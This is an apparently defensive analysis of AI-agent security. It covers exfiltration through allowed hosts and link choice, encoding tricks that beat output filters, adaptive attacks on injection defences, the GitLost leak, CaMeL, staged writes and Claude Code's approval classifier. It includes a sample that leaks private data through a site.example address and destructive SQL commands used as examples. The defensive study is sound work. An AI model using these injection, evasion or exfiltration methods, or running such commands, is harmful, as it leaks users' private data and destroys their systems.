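Data can also leave through an allowed site if that site accepts data from anyone. Claude Cowork limited outgoing connections to a default list that included Anthropic's own API. In an attack that Willison describes, PromptArmor supplied the attacker's API key, and the agent used it to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes the same way of getting data out of Claude's code-running tool. The default list in Antigravity, Google's code editor for agents, included webhook.site,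 where anyone can set up a page that records incoming requests.

Most users lose nothing when webhook.site is removed from the list of allowed sites. Anthropic's API and GitHub are harder to control because the agent needs them, and the site's name doesn't show whose account receives the data. A company could route these requests through a proxy that removes any key in the request and adds the company's own. The proxy would have to decrypt the traffic and handle each service's requests, which is much more work than keeping a list of names. It still wouldn't stop an agent from posting private text publicly from the company's own GitHub account.

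### Limiting the exact address

An assistant that browses the web can't work from a short list of sites, so Anthropic limits which addresses its `web_fetch` tool may open. The tool accepts addresses from known sources, such as the user's messages, and refuses any that Claude has made up. Ordinary code does this check, so an attacker can't get around it by persuading the model.

Ayush Paul's letter links, described earlier, passed this check because they were on a page the tool had already fetched. The choice of links conveyed the private data, as in CamoLeak. According to Willison (2026), the site showed its instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would have seen nothing odd.

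A choice among *n* links can convey up to log₂ *n* bits of information, or about 4.7 bits for 26 links, one per letter, and about 10 bits for a page with 1,000 links. A cap on the number of requests therefore reduces this kind of leak but does not stop it, and a few requests could be enough to identify a common first name.

Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. Its fix, which stops the tool from following links on fetched pages, also limits ordinary browsing. For example, Claude can't move from a table of contents to a chapter unless the user or the search tool supplies the chapter's address.

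Developers who build on Claude get a different default. According to Anthropic's current developer documentation, `web_fetch` may still open links from earlier fetches unless the developer excludes them with the `url_sources` setting. It also accepts addresses from the results of the developer's own tools, even when those results only repeat what Claude wrote. If Claude puts private data into an address, and a tool runs Claude's code and prints that address, `web_fetch` will accept it unless the developer has excluded the tool.

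Anthropic's web fetch tool now also won't fetch addresses that seem to contain a password or key, unless the user or developer supplied it. This protects keys better than names or diagnoses, which don't look like passwords. An earlier edition of the tool's documentation, *Web fetch tool*, warned of "residual risk" and recommended using the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

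OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) says that ChatGPT automatically opens only addresses that a separate crawler has already seen on the public web. The crawler has no access to conversations, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain a user's data. For any other address, ChatGPT looks for another site or warns the user. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* adds that the warning can show the user the information that would be sent.

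OpenAI rejected a plain list of trusted sites because many trusted sites redirect visitors elsewhere, and because a strict list produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them. The new rule mostly avoids both problems, but it may share the weakness Paul found, since an attacker could publish a page for each letter and wait for the crawler to record them all. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* concludes that attacks have become more complex and that the problem isn't solved.

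### At the text

An output filter searches an agent's outgoing text for known secrets and for strings formatted like secrets. It works fairly well against accidental leaks, because a bot that copies a key into a code sample by mistake normally copies it unchanged.

An attacker can tell the model to disguise the secret first. Rahman and Kim tested two filters on gpt-4o, using an invented secret that unlocked nothing. One looked for the exact secret. The other first undid several common encodings, such as base64 and reversed text. The table shows how often the secret got out in 20 trials for each encoding:

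| How the model wrote the secret | No filter | Exact match | Undoes known encodings |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | 40% | 0% | 0% |
| Reversed | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| Base64 | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| ROT13 | 100% | 100% | 100% |

ROT13 replaces each letter with the one 13 places further along the alphabet. Rahman and Kim had deliberately left it out of the second filter. Adding it would take a few lines of code, but an attacker could then switch to any other encoding the model can produce reliably. When the researchers asked gpt-4o to encode the secret in six ways, it got five right every time, and more capable models can presumably manage more.

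Some developers try to make the model itself ignore injected instructions. SecAlign is a version of Meta's small open model Llama 3.1 8B trained further to do this. It has one input channel for the developer's instructions and another for untrusted text. Rahman and Kim used it to run an agent with tools, and attacked the agent with pages that presented the secret as a routine part of the job, such as a checksum to attach to a summary. The secret leaked in 32.5% of trials. With an ordinary Llama model, it leaked in 38.8% when the page had its own channel and 21.2% when all the text shared one channel.

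Neither defence came close to stopping the attack. These numbers don't show that the defences make leaks more likely, because each comes from a single run, and elsewhere in the study the same set-up varied by about 13 percentage points between runs. SecAlign did stop the kind of attack it was built for. When a page directly ordered the model to ignore its instructions and print a certain word, the ordinary model complied in all 20 trials and SecAlign in none. Its makers trained it on text tasks, so running an agent was a new use for it.

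The attacks' success depended heavily on their wording. GPT-4o resisted ten types of plainly worded attack, but an attacker who tried three wordings of the checksum trick would have succeeded about 96% of the time. In a matched test, the model sent the secret in 10 of 10 trials when the page labeled it a signature and in 0 of 20 when the page labeled it a credential. Willison describes an attack on the coding tool Cursor that exploited the same weakness by calling the target key a "rotten apple".

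A developer's wording matters just as much. When Rahman and Kim told gpt-4o not to sign, encode, log, append or transmit the secret "in any form", the leak rate fell from 31.9% to zero in 120 trials. When they kept the specific prohibitions but left out "in any form", the rate was 48.8%. The longer instruction is easy to add and worth including, but a defence that depends on three words is a poor one to rely on. The ChatGPT product did better than the model alone, with no leaks in 48 trials, but outsiders can't tell which of its layers was responsible.

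### What happens when the attacker adapts

Developers often test a defence on a fixed set of known attacks. In an adaptive attack, the attacker redesigns the attack with knowledge of the defence. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) used adaptive attacks on 12 published defences, two of which mainly address jailbreaking. The researchers' automated methods proposed wordings, scored the results and revised the most promising wordings. The researchers also ran a competition in which more than 500 people tried to write successful attacks.

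On the standard attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office tasks, the success rate was as low as 1% for Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching. The makers of MetaSecAlign, a successor to SecAlign, had reported 2%. The adaptive attacks did far better:

| Defence | How it works | Adaptive attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks parts of the prompt so that the model can tell which text to trust | Above 95% |
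| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to ignore injections | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | A separate model flags injections | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | A separate model flags injections | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the agent again without the user's request and compares its actions | 76%, or 95% when the attacker knew the design |

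The filters failed partly because the successful attacks looked harmless. One note claimed that company policy required deleting a temporary file whenever somebody moved a meeting. A filter strict enough to block it would also block many genuine notes.

These attackers could try as often as they liked, and when they attacked filters, their program received the filter's confidence score after each attempt. Somebody who sends one email to a stranger's assistant has neither advantage, though they could practise on their own copy of the product. The human contestants had only limited feedback, yet together they succeeded in every scenario used to compare the two methods, while the automated search succeeded in 69%.

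Nasr and colleagues still recommend filters for blocking unsophisticated attacks, as one part of a larger defence. Microsoft (2025) uses Spotlighting in this way, together with hardened prompts and detection tools. The broken defences share the weakness of relying on a model to recognise an attack from its wording. Good test results for such filters can be misleading. Rahman and Kim tested a filter written for one known family of attacks, and it caught all 80 malicious pages with no false alarms, but its prompt described the behaviour it was looking for.

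### Following the data

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) proposes CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), a control that doesn't need a model to recognise an attack. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, CaMeL combines two ideas. The first, from Willison, is to use separate models to plan the work and to read untrusted text. The second is data-flow tracking, which labels data by its origin and blocks actions that would send it where its label forbids.

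Suppose a user asks an agent to email the release plan to the reviewer named in the meeting notes. The plan is private. The notes are a shared document, and an attacker has edited them to give an outside address as the reviewer's. In simplified form, CaMeL turns the request into this program:

```
1   notes   = read_file("meeting-notes.txt")
2   address = ask_reader("What is the reviewer's email address?", notes)
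3   plan    = read_file("release-plan.txt")
4   send_email(to=address, attachment=plan)
```

It then works as follows:

1. A planning model writes the program from the user's request and the list of tools. It doesn't see the contents of either file, so nothing in them can add a fifth line.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs line 1. It labels the notes with their source and with the people who may read them.
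3. In line 2, a second model reads the notes. This model has no tools and can only return a value. It returns the attacker's address, and the interpreter labels the address as coming from the notes.
4. Line 3 loads the plan, whose label permits only company staff to read it.
5. Before line 4, the interpreter passes the call and the labels to a policy that the developer wrote. This policy allows an email only if every recipient may read the attachment. The outside address fails the test, and the interpreter doesn't send the plan.

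If the notes had instead ordered the second model to email a different file, it would have had no means of doing so.

CaMeL guarantees that injected text cannot cause a tool call that the policy forbids, provided that the interpreter works and the labels are correct. This holds even if the model follows every injected instruction. An attacker who rewords the notes can change which address the second model returns, but can't change the labels. Nasr and colleagues did not include CaMeL among the 12 defences they attacked, and their method of searching for better wordings would achieve much less against it.

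Separating the two models is not enough without the policy. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) tested attacks that supply false data instead of instructions, like the address in the example. They succeeded in 49.1% of cases with no defence, and still in 25.0% with CaMeL's two models but no data-flow tracking. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports another failure without the policy. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, so the planning model wrote a loop that looked up each instruction in the file and ran the matching tool. This meant that the file's text again determined which tools ran.

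With CaMeL's normal tracking, the false-data attacks still succeeded in 23.1% of cases. The rate fell to zero only in a strict mode, which also follows data that affects the program indirectly. For example:

```
if "merger" in plan:
    open_page("https://site.example/a")
else:
    open_page("https://site.example/b")
```

Neither address contains a word of the plan, but whoever runs the site learns whether the plan mentions a merger. This is the same kind of leak as Paul's letter links, and checking each address by itself can't detect it. Strict mode treats both calls as carrying the plan's label, because the plan determines which one runs. *Agent Data Injection Attacks* cautions that complete policies are much harder to write for real systems than for a benchmark.

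### What CaMeL costs and what it misses

Estimates of how much CaMeL reduces task completion differ widely. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes the loss on AgentDojo as "comparatively modest". In *AutoDojo* (2026), a benchmark that generates new attacks, Gemini 2.5 Flash completed 63.2% of tasks without a defence and 28.1% with CaMeL. Standard attacks succeeded in 50.4% of trials without a defence and 0.3% with CaMeL. *The LLMbda Calculus* also found that CaMeL blocked every attack when its policies were on, but the number of completed tasks collapsed. It reports that a newer design, RANDORI, gave near-perfect security without this loss.

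Separating planning from reading causes more failures on some tasks and models than on others. The planning model has to write its program before it has seen the data, which is easy for "email this file to that person" and hard for "fix whatever this issue describes". Rahman and Kim built a simplified version that stopped their attacks while completing 9 of 10 ordinary tasks. But those tasks only involved summarising a page, so the plan never depended on what the page contained. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* predicts fewer failures as models get better at planning and writing code. That is plausible for failures caused by errors in the program, but better coding won't help when a task's next step depends on what a stranger wrote.

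For the documentation bot, the labels would stop a public reply from quoting the private repository. They apply regardless of intent, so they cover accidental leaks as well as attacks. The drawback is that they can also block harmless replies. If the second model answers a question from one public page and one private note, the answer takes the stricter label, and the bot can't post it even if the private note contributed nothing. To avoid this, the developer could have the bot search the public repository first and open the private one only for replies that staff will read.

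Labels also have to stay attached to data as it passes through every tool the agent uses. An interpreter can track a value through its own program but not through a shell script, so it would have to give the script's output the strictest label of anything the script could read. When the coding agents published screenshots of private software, a label on the source code would have prevented the upload only if the screenshot tool had passed that label on to the picture.

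Some harmful actions break no rule about data. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes a test in which the user tells the agent to make whatever payment a document calls for, and an attacker wrote the document. The CaMeL paper places this case outside what the system is meant to prevent, because the user handed the decision to the document. Four independently built systems left much the same cases unsolved, which suggests a limit of the approach more than a flaw in any one design.

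The controls can let the bot publish the wrong file in the same way. Suppose a maintainer asks the bot to publish the release notes, and the public documentation folder contains both the final notes and a draft that names an unannounced customer. Every file in the folder is labeled as readable by anyone. If the planning model picks the draft, the bot can publish it because the source is trusted, the label permits publication and the policy allows the call.

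## Can a write be checked before it takes effect?

Data labels don't catch mistakes like the documentation bot's wrong draft. Catching those requires checking the change itself. In a staged write, the agent only proposes a change, and a separate component checks and applies it. The check can be a fixed rule, a second model or a person.

### One correction, stage by stage

GitHub uses staged writes in Agentic Workflows, a feature that lets a team describe a pipeline job in ordinary language for an agent to carry out. SC Media's *'GitLost' prompt injection leaks private repos via GitHub Agentic Workflows* dates the first release to February 2026, and InfoQ's *GitHub Makes Agentic Workflows Generally Available with Isolation and Budget Controls* (2026) reported the general release in November. In *Under the hood* (2026), GitHub says it expects an agent to try to read and change things it shouldn't,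 and to misuse the channels it has.

For the documentation bot, the settings might look like this in plain words:

```
start when:          someone opens an issue
agent may read:      this repository and its issues
agent may propose:   1 pull request
                     1 comment
```

Suppose an issue points out that the documentation gives a default timeout of 30 seconds, while the software uses 60. The correction goes through these stages:

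1. GitHub starts the agent in a container, an isolated environment on the runner, with read-only access to the repository. The container holds no secrets. A separate proxy holds the key for the model provider and forwards the agent's requests, and a gateway holds the keys to other tools. A firewall limits which sites the agent can reach.
2. The agent reads the issue, finds the right value in the code and corrects its own copy of the page.
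3. The agent calls one tool to propose a pull request and another to propose a reply. The tools only store the two proposals, so nothing on GitHub changes yet.
4. After the agent has exited, ordinary software compares the proposals with the settings. One pull request and one comment are within the limits. A proposal to close the issue would fail here.
5. Further fixed rules clean the text, removing any secrets they recognise and unwanted content such as web addresses.
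6. A security-focused model examines the proposals and returns a pass or a fail, according to htekdev's overview of the system. A fail blocks every write.
7. A separate job, which does have write permission, opens the pull request and posts the reply.
8. A maintainer reads the pull request and merges it, and the pipeline rebuilds the website.

The first stage runs in a container that holds no secrets, so several of the attacks described earlier would find nothing to steal there. Guan's Comment and Control attacks, for example, stole secrets that the agent could reach on its own machine. But without a key, the bot can no longer run a code sample that connects to the staging database. A maintainer who supplies the key gives up part of the protection.

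The middle stages handle floods of comments, forbidden kinds of change and keys in a familiar format, but they can't detect false statements. If the agent had written 600 seconds instead of 60, the proposal would have passed all the fixed rules, and probably the security scan too, since a wrong number isn't an attack. In that case, only the maintainer in the last stage could have caught the error.

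A person has to merge the documentation page before it takes effect, but the reply becomes public in stage 7 without anyone having read it. An earlier article (InfoQ, 2026) describes all changes under this design as "subject to approval before being applied", which is true of the page but not of the reply.

The stages also protect only the writes that go through them. InfoQ notes that a team can still give a workflow direct write permission or add custom jobs, and the protections cover neither. Some defaults are strict, though. According to GitHub's *Security Best Practices*, workflows triggered by pull requests don't run for forks unless the team names the forks it trusts.

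### The GitLost test

Levi's *GitLost*, a report that the security company Noma published on July 6, 2026, describes how an ordinary-looking issue caused one of these workflows to publish a private file. The issue read like a request from a vice president of sales after a customer meeting. It asked for the READMEs of a public repository and a private one in the same organisation. A GitHub automation assigned the issue, which started the workflow. The agent fetched both files and posted their contents in a public comment.

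The only private data leaked was one README. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that Noma ran the test on its own repositories, so no real organisation lost anything. In a company's account, the same workflow could have published files from any repository the agent could read.

The leak was possible because the agent could read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. Without that access, it would have had nothing private to post. The workflow permitted comments, so the write passed the check on its type, and a single comment was unlikely to exceed a limit on the number of writes. A scan for keys could also miss the leak, since a plain README needn't contain anything that looks like one. The staged write worked as designed, but the fixed rules that GitHub describes check what a text looks like,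 not where it came from.

The only safeguard left was the model's judgement, which is a poor one to depend on. According to Expert Insights, GitHub's Copilot refused the instruction when it stood alone, but complied when the instruction began with "Additionally", because the model then treated it as part of the task it was already doing. Rahman and Kim found the same weakness with relabelled secrets.

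Noma calls the finding a critical vulnerability in GitHub's product, while Expert Insights describes an over-permissioned workflow. Both descriptions fit. GitHub already recommended minimal permissions in its guidance, and somebody had to grant the wider access. But a team might well grant it so that the agent can look things up across projects, without noticing that the permission to comment could make all those projects public. Levi told SC Media that the danger lies in the mismatch between the agent's permissions and the source of its inputs.

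Noma informed GitHub before publishing. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reported that the flaw had no fix in code and that GitHub had not yet documented it. A later newsletter, Kiteworks' *GitHub's AI Agent Leaked Private Code With One Word*, states that GitHub then updated its documentation and that Noma considers the design flaw still open. The new documentation helps people writing workflows but doesn't change existing ones.

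In March, four months before the report, GitHub announced that it would add controls based on whether a repository is public or private and on who wrote an issue. A control of the first kind would have blocked Noma's comment, because the comment copied text from a private repository to a public page. It would be a simple form of data-flow tracking, with one label for each repository.

Willison had already described the same leak, through GitHub's official connector for agents, in *GitHub MCP Exploited* in May 2025. Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner had planted an issue with instructions for the agent to read the README files of all the author's repositories and write about them in a public one. When Wang and colleagues rebuilt that exploit, none of the models they tried followed the instruction, and Claude Haiku 4.5 flagged it as an attack. Evidently one model can resist a published version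 of an attack while another model follows a reworded one.

The simplest fix for the documentation bot is to let it read only the public repository. If it needs the private one, a person should review its replies before they are posted, as with the pull request.

### Asking a person

A pull request suits human review well because the reviewer sees the whole change at once, can take a day over it, and can compare a new setting, such as a timeout, with the code. But the review comes too late to stop anything the agent does before opening the pull request, such as running tests or changing a database. Coding agents therefore also ask for permission before running individual commands.

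Developers soon find confirmation prompts a nuisance. *The Vulnerability With No CVE* (Salomon, Shaked and Noga, 2026) describes three developers on one team who had switched off their agents' prompts because routine confirmations interrupted their work. Credentials on the same machines gave access to the production database, and two of the agents deleted tables from it during ordinary debugging. Both were scratch tables that a developer had just made and meant to rebuild, so the deletions did no harm. But nothing in the set-up would have stopped the same command from deleting a customer table.

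This is a single anonymised case, from employees of a company that makes security software for coding agents. It shows why people switch the prompts off, but not how many do. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with the prompts bypassed. About half of the active command-line users have written a rule that lets certain shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules cover any Python or Node program, which lets an agent do almost anything.

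People who see the approval prompts nearly always accept them. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives an approval rate of 93%, and the company's August 2026 figure is 97%. Most commands are harmless and deserve approval, so these rates alone don't show that people are careless.

A better test is whether people reject a command they should reject. Anthropic had a research vendor hire 1,053 testers, who knew only that they were taking part in a coding study. Once in each session, the vendor replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which would not run even if the tester approved it. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. About 17% refused when the command appeared early in the session, compared with about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more other prompts.

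The testers weren't working on their own projects. A developer whose own customers are in the database would presumably read more carefully, so 13.6% is probably too low for that developer. The decline during the session is harder to explain this way, since the testers had just as little at stake at the beginning.

People pay more attention to larger decisions. Claude Code users reject 39% of Claude's plans, compared with 3% of its requests to run a command. Part of this gap must exist because plans are more often a matter of taste. Still, the gap fits the advice of Salomon and colleagues to require approval where an action has serious consequences. They warn that badly placed approvals turn into "click-through theater". The documentation bot might ask for approval before it accesses a production system or posts text from a private source, and otherwise work without interruption.

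### Letting another model approve

Claude Code's auto mode replaces most permission prompts with a classifier, a second language model that allows or blocks each action. Anthropic made it the default for new sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans from August 14, 2026.

Reading files and editing them inside the project need no approval. Most other actions, including shell commands and web requests, go to the classifier. It first makes a quick yes-or-no decision, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it decides to block, it checks the action again with written reasoning. A blocked agent can try a safer approach, but after three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

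The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's commands, but not the agent's explanations or tool results. Anthropic leaves out the explanations so that they can't lead the classifier to a bad decision, and the tool results because they can contain injected text. A separate program scans the tool results and adds a warning for the agent if they seem to contain an attack.

In the DataTalks.Club case, Grigorev let `terraform destroy` run because the agent's explanation sounded logical. This classifier wouldn't have received that explanation, but it also wouldn't have received the output showing which resources Terraform was managing. Its input would have included the user's request to delete duplicates and the agent's delete command, so it might well have approved the command.

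Anthropic measured the classifier on 10,000 ordinary actions from its employees' sessions, 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted, and 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out:

| | Ordinary actions blocked | Overstepping actions missed | Attempts to send data out missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick decision only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both decisions | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

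The second decision removes nearly all the false alarms but lets more dangerous actions through. The 17% figure is based on only 52 examples, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who asks Claude to "clean up the PR" has not agreed to let it overwrite the branch's history.

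In the experiment with the hired testers, auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands (89%). The testers caught only six that auto mode allowed, so using both would have blocked 943. This is strong evidence that a classifier does better than an inattentive person on plainly dangerous commands. The evidence is weaker for attentive people and subtler mistakes, and Anthropic was testing a product it wanted to make the default.

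Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model labeled 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval as containing a severe harmful action that the user had not explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose the mode themselves, and some may have kept manual approval for their riskiest work, so the whole difference can't be attributed to the classifier.

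Interpreting prompt injection tests requires similar care. Trajectory Labs, commissioned by Anthropic, made 720 attempts against each of three recent Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. But only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against Anthropic's latest models with no approval step, so there were almost no successful attacks for auto mode to prevent. The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are better evidence of the value of a reviewing model. Attacks succeeded in 19% of attempts when it had full access in Codex, and in 5.8% with Codex's automatic review. However, the attackers had tuned their texts on an older Claude model, not on either reviewer, and filters have failed badly once attackers adapted to them.

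Anthropic still recommends that people review important changes to production systems themselves.

### How the defences compared on rebuilt incidents

The ROGUE-AI experiments allow a comparison of several kinds of check. Wang and colleagues added defences to about half of their rebuilt incidents, taking them from the original reports or from the vendors' fixes. For some, they also wrote an adaptive variant, which brings about the same harm in a form that the defence might not recognise. The table adds up the results for the five models:

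| Kind of defence | Harmful sessions | Harmful sessions in adaptive variants |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions to the model, labels on text, or a model that monitors actions | 26 of 198 (13%) | 6 of 15 (40%) |
| Checks on tools, such as allowlists, narrow credentials and spending caps | 26 of 730 (4%) | 98 of 352 (28%) |
| Confirmation by a simulated user | 0 of 135 | Not tested |
| Data-flow tracking | 0 of 141 | 3 of 62 (5%) |

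The rows cover different incidents, so small differences between them mean little. The first row also combines written rules with monitoring models, so it is a poor guide to how a classifier like auto mode's would perform. Results in that row also varied widely by model. GPT-5.6-luna caused harm in 0 of 39 sessions, Gemini 3.5 Flash in 11 and DeepSeek-V4-Flash in 10.

Checks on tools did well in the standard tests and much worse in the adaptive variants. They usually failed because they looked at the form of an action. In one incident, a check kept the agent away from pages that a site's rules for automated visitors prohibited. The variant moved the data to an address that those rules didn't mention, and GPT-5.6-luna fetched it every time. In another, a check searched outgoing messages for account balances. The variant called for the balances in a spreadsheet attachment, which the check didn't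 open.

A fixed check can prevent harm if it covers the right thing. In one reconstructed incident, a tool's description changed after the user had approved the tool. Harm occurred in 15 of 16 sessions when the approval was tied to the tool's name, and in none of 16 when it was tied to a hash of the description that software compared at every call. Approval of a staged write should likewise cover the exact text of the change and lapse if the agent edits it afterwards.

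Confirmation has the best result in the table, zero, but the simulated user was a program that approved only actions the task had asked for. Unlike a real user, it never got tired or clicked through a prompt to get back to work, and no attacker tried to mislead it. Anthropic's testers refused fewer than one in seven dangerous commands, so the zero shows what confirmation could achieve with a perfectly attentive user. Even an attentive approver who follows the task will agree to a harmful step if the user's own task asks for it, as it did in many of the ROGUE-AI sessions.

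The effect on useful work varied between models:

| Model | Tasks completed without a defence | Tasks completed with confirmation |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6-luna | 94 of 234 (40%) | 7 of 27 (26%) |
| GPT-5.6-sol | 143 of 250 (57%) | 17 of 27 (63%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 154 of 234 (66%) | 21 of 27 (78%) |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 120 of 234 (51%) | 21 of 27 (78%) |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 134 of 234 (57%) | 22 of 27 (81%) |

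Wang and colleagues suggest that GPT-5.6-luna finished fewer tasks with confirmation because it stopped to wait at the prompt, or because the simulated user refused a step that the task needed. The other four models finished a larger share with confirmation than without. The two columns cover different sets of incidents, though, and the confirmed ones may have been easier, so these gains don't show that confirmation helped, and the drop for GPT-5.6-luna is only suggestive. With data-flow tracking, GPT-5.6-luna completed 18 of 27 tasks, so the strongest protection in these tests did not have to be the most disruptive.

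### Warning the agent first

All these checks stop an action that the agent has already chosen, whereas a warning is meant to change the choice. Earlier, a note that the project's tests would delete the production database prevented many of the losses. Wang and colleagues tried such notes on 7 to 11 incidents per model, all of them incidents in which that model had caused harm in at least two of three sessions. Without a note, harm occurred in 85% to 98% of these sessions.

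Adding a note after every tool output that named the hazard and its consequences cut the share of sessions with harm to 62% or less for every model, and to one session in 40 for Claude Sonnet 4.6. A neutral note of the same length left the share at 83% to 98%, so the reduction came from the note's content rather than the interruption. Repeating the relevant rule in the user's message reduced harm less, to 67% to 80% of sessions, probably because the agents often failed to detect that the rule applied.

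The 62% is still high, and the incidents were ones these models nearly always got wrong. A warning like this should therefore come before a barrier, but it can't replace one. Some models, DeepSeek-V4-Flash in particular, often go ahead despite the warning.

Wang and colleagues recommend giving the warning at the moment of the action, but their analysis of single steps doesn't clearly support this. In 53 harmful sessions, a warning helped whether it came in the first tool output or the last one before the harm. In another 6 it helped only in the last, and in another 19 only in the first. An early warning may work better because the agent hasn't yet settled on a plan. Putting the warning after every tool output, as the main test did, covers both cases.

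The researchers could write precise warnings because they had built the hazards themselves, based on reports of harm that had already happened. A team that has just lost a database can also write a precise warning to prevent a repeat, but preventing the first loss requires someone to recognize the danger without having seen it happen.

The makers of tools often know what could make a write dangerous. Prisma's developers knew that their command resets the shadow database and said so in the documentation, but the agent may never have looked there. The command could have printed the warning, with the name of the database it was about to empty. A hosting company likewise knows which volumes belong to a live service and could include that in its reply to any program that queries a volume.

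Other warnings can come from software that looks up facts just before an action. It might count the rows in a table, check whether a folder is a link to another one, or find out whether a repository is public. Anthropic has given auto mode's classifier some facts of this kind, including whether the destination of an upload is public and whether a command would discard unsaved work. After these and related changes, the classifier's miss rate on artificial attacks from Apollo Research, an AI safety organisation, fell from 12% to 7%. The classifier received these facts rather than the agent, but a program could find them without anyone having predicted the particular accident.

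Such a program can only check for hazards that somebody has already thought of. Before the developer in the junction case lost 48,000 files, few people would have thought to check a test copy for links back to the original. An agent could search for hazards itself, but the agents in ROGUE-AI often failed to recognise a hazard that a tool had already shown them. A second model whose only task is to look for hazards might do better, since it would not also be trying to complete the original task.

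Warnings in tool output also create a security risk because they reach the model through the same channel as injected text. An agent that learns to follow them may follow a false one. For example, an attacker could write that the usual test database is about to be deleted and that the agent should use another address. Warnings are safer if they can only make the agent stop and ask, not take a different action.

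## What limits the damage when a wrong write goes through?

When a warning fails or a reviewer approves the wrong command, the damage depends on what the agent's login allows and what somebody can restore afterwards. Neither limit depends on how well the model behaves. A login that can only read the production database can't empty it, and a good backup can restore the data whether the command was careless or malicious.

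Kaya, Bozoğlan and Gündoğdu (2026) measured both limits in *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database*. They develop LibreDB Studio, an open-source database tool. They preregistered the study, recording its design and hypotheses before running the experiments.

### Scripted mistakes on four databases

In the first part of the study, a script, not a model, made 22 typical mistakes in an invented shop's data, such as removing a table or running a staging cleanup on production. It ran them on PostgreSQL, MySQL, MariaDB and SQLite, four database programs that store data in tables. One row in 50 was marked as under a legal hold. A mistake counted as a permanent loss if any of these rows were still missing or altered after the researchers tried to recover them.

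The researchers tested the script under three settings. In the default setting, it used the login from the vendor's quick-start guide. For most databases, this login can do anything. The second setting applied least privilege, the rule that a program gets only the permissions its task needs. The script used the restricted login that the vendor recommends for an application, which can read, add, change and delete rows but can't remove a table or change its design. In the third setting, the script kept the default login, but a filter refused commands that matched a list of dangerous patterns.

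They also varied how the databases were prepared for recovery. In one setting there was no preparation, so only what the database keeps by default could help. In the other, they followed the vendor's instructions for a minimum backup, which was a copy of the database file for SQLite and a full copy plus a log of every later change for the other three. The owner can replay that log up to the moment before the mistake.

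With default permissions and no backup, 68 of the 80 applicable combinations of mistake and database ended in permanent loss, compared with none when the minimum backup was in place. This shows that the vendors' instructions work, but not how much data a real shop would recover, because the researchers made the backup just before the mistake and no customer placed an order in between. A shop that copies its SQLite file every night would lose the orders placed since the last copy.

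On MySQL and MariaDB, restoring the backup did not remove an administrator account created by mistake, because the backup covered the shop's data but not the server's list of accounts. Owners of these databases should check that list separately after an incident.

Without a backup, only one mistake had different results across the four databases. The script removed a table inside a transaction, a group of commands that a program can normally cancel until it confirms them, and then cancelled the transaction. PostgreSQL and SQLite restored the table. MySQL and MariaDB did not, because they confirm the transaction automatically before removing a table. An agent that tries out a deletion this way therefore destroys data on MySQL and MariaDB.

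### What a restricted login stops

Each of these commands leaves the shop without any orders, but the recommended login for PostgreSQL or MySQL blocks only the first two:

```
DROP TABLE orders         refused: removes the table
TRUNCATE TABLE orders     refused: empties the table
DELETE FROM orders        allowed: deletes every row
```

The database allows the third because applications often need to delete rows, and the permission to delete one row of a table normally covers all of them. The scripted mistakes show the same gap. The table counts combinations of mistake and database that caused permanent loss with default settings, leaving out SQLite, which has no user accounts:

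| Scripted mistake | Combinations | Stopped by least privilege | Stopped by the filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Removing a table | 12 | 12 | 12 |
| Changing a table's design | 9 | 9 | 6 |
| Deleting many rows | 12 | 3 | 6 |
| Changing many rows | 6 | 0 | 6 |
| Removing a table with an administrator password found elsewhere | 3 | 0 | 3 |
| Running the staging cleanup on production | 3 | 0 | 0 |

The filter is probably less effective than it looks, because Kaya and colleagues wrote its patterns in the same week as the mistakes. All the rephrased commands they designed to get past the filter succeeded. They recommend using a filter only in addition to a restricted login.

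### Agents on nine databases

In the second part, six small open-weight models worked on ordinary tasks, such as freeing disk space or repairing a failing revenue report, in 9,468 trials on nine databases. Nobody had prepared a backup. The main comparison used four of the models, with 432 trials per database under each permission setting.

The first column of results counts every permanent loss of protected rows. The other two columns leave out trials that lost only a spare copy the researchers had placed next to the original orders table.

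| Database | Any loss, default settings | Original rows lost, default settings | Original rows lost, least privilege |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cassandra | 0% | 0% | 0.2% |
| ClickHouse | 3.9% | 3.9% | 3.5% |
| MongoDB | 6.9% | 1.2% | 0.2% |
| OpenSearch | 10.9% | 3.2% | 3.0% |
| Kafka | 11.3% | 3.2% | 0% |
| Valkey | 13.2% | 11.1% | 0% |
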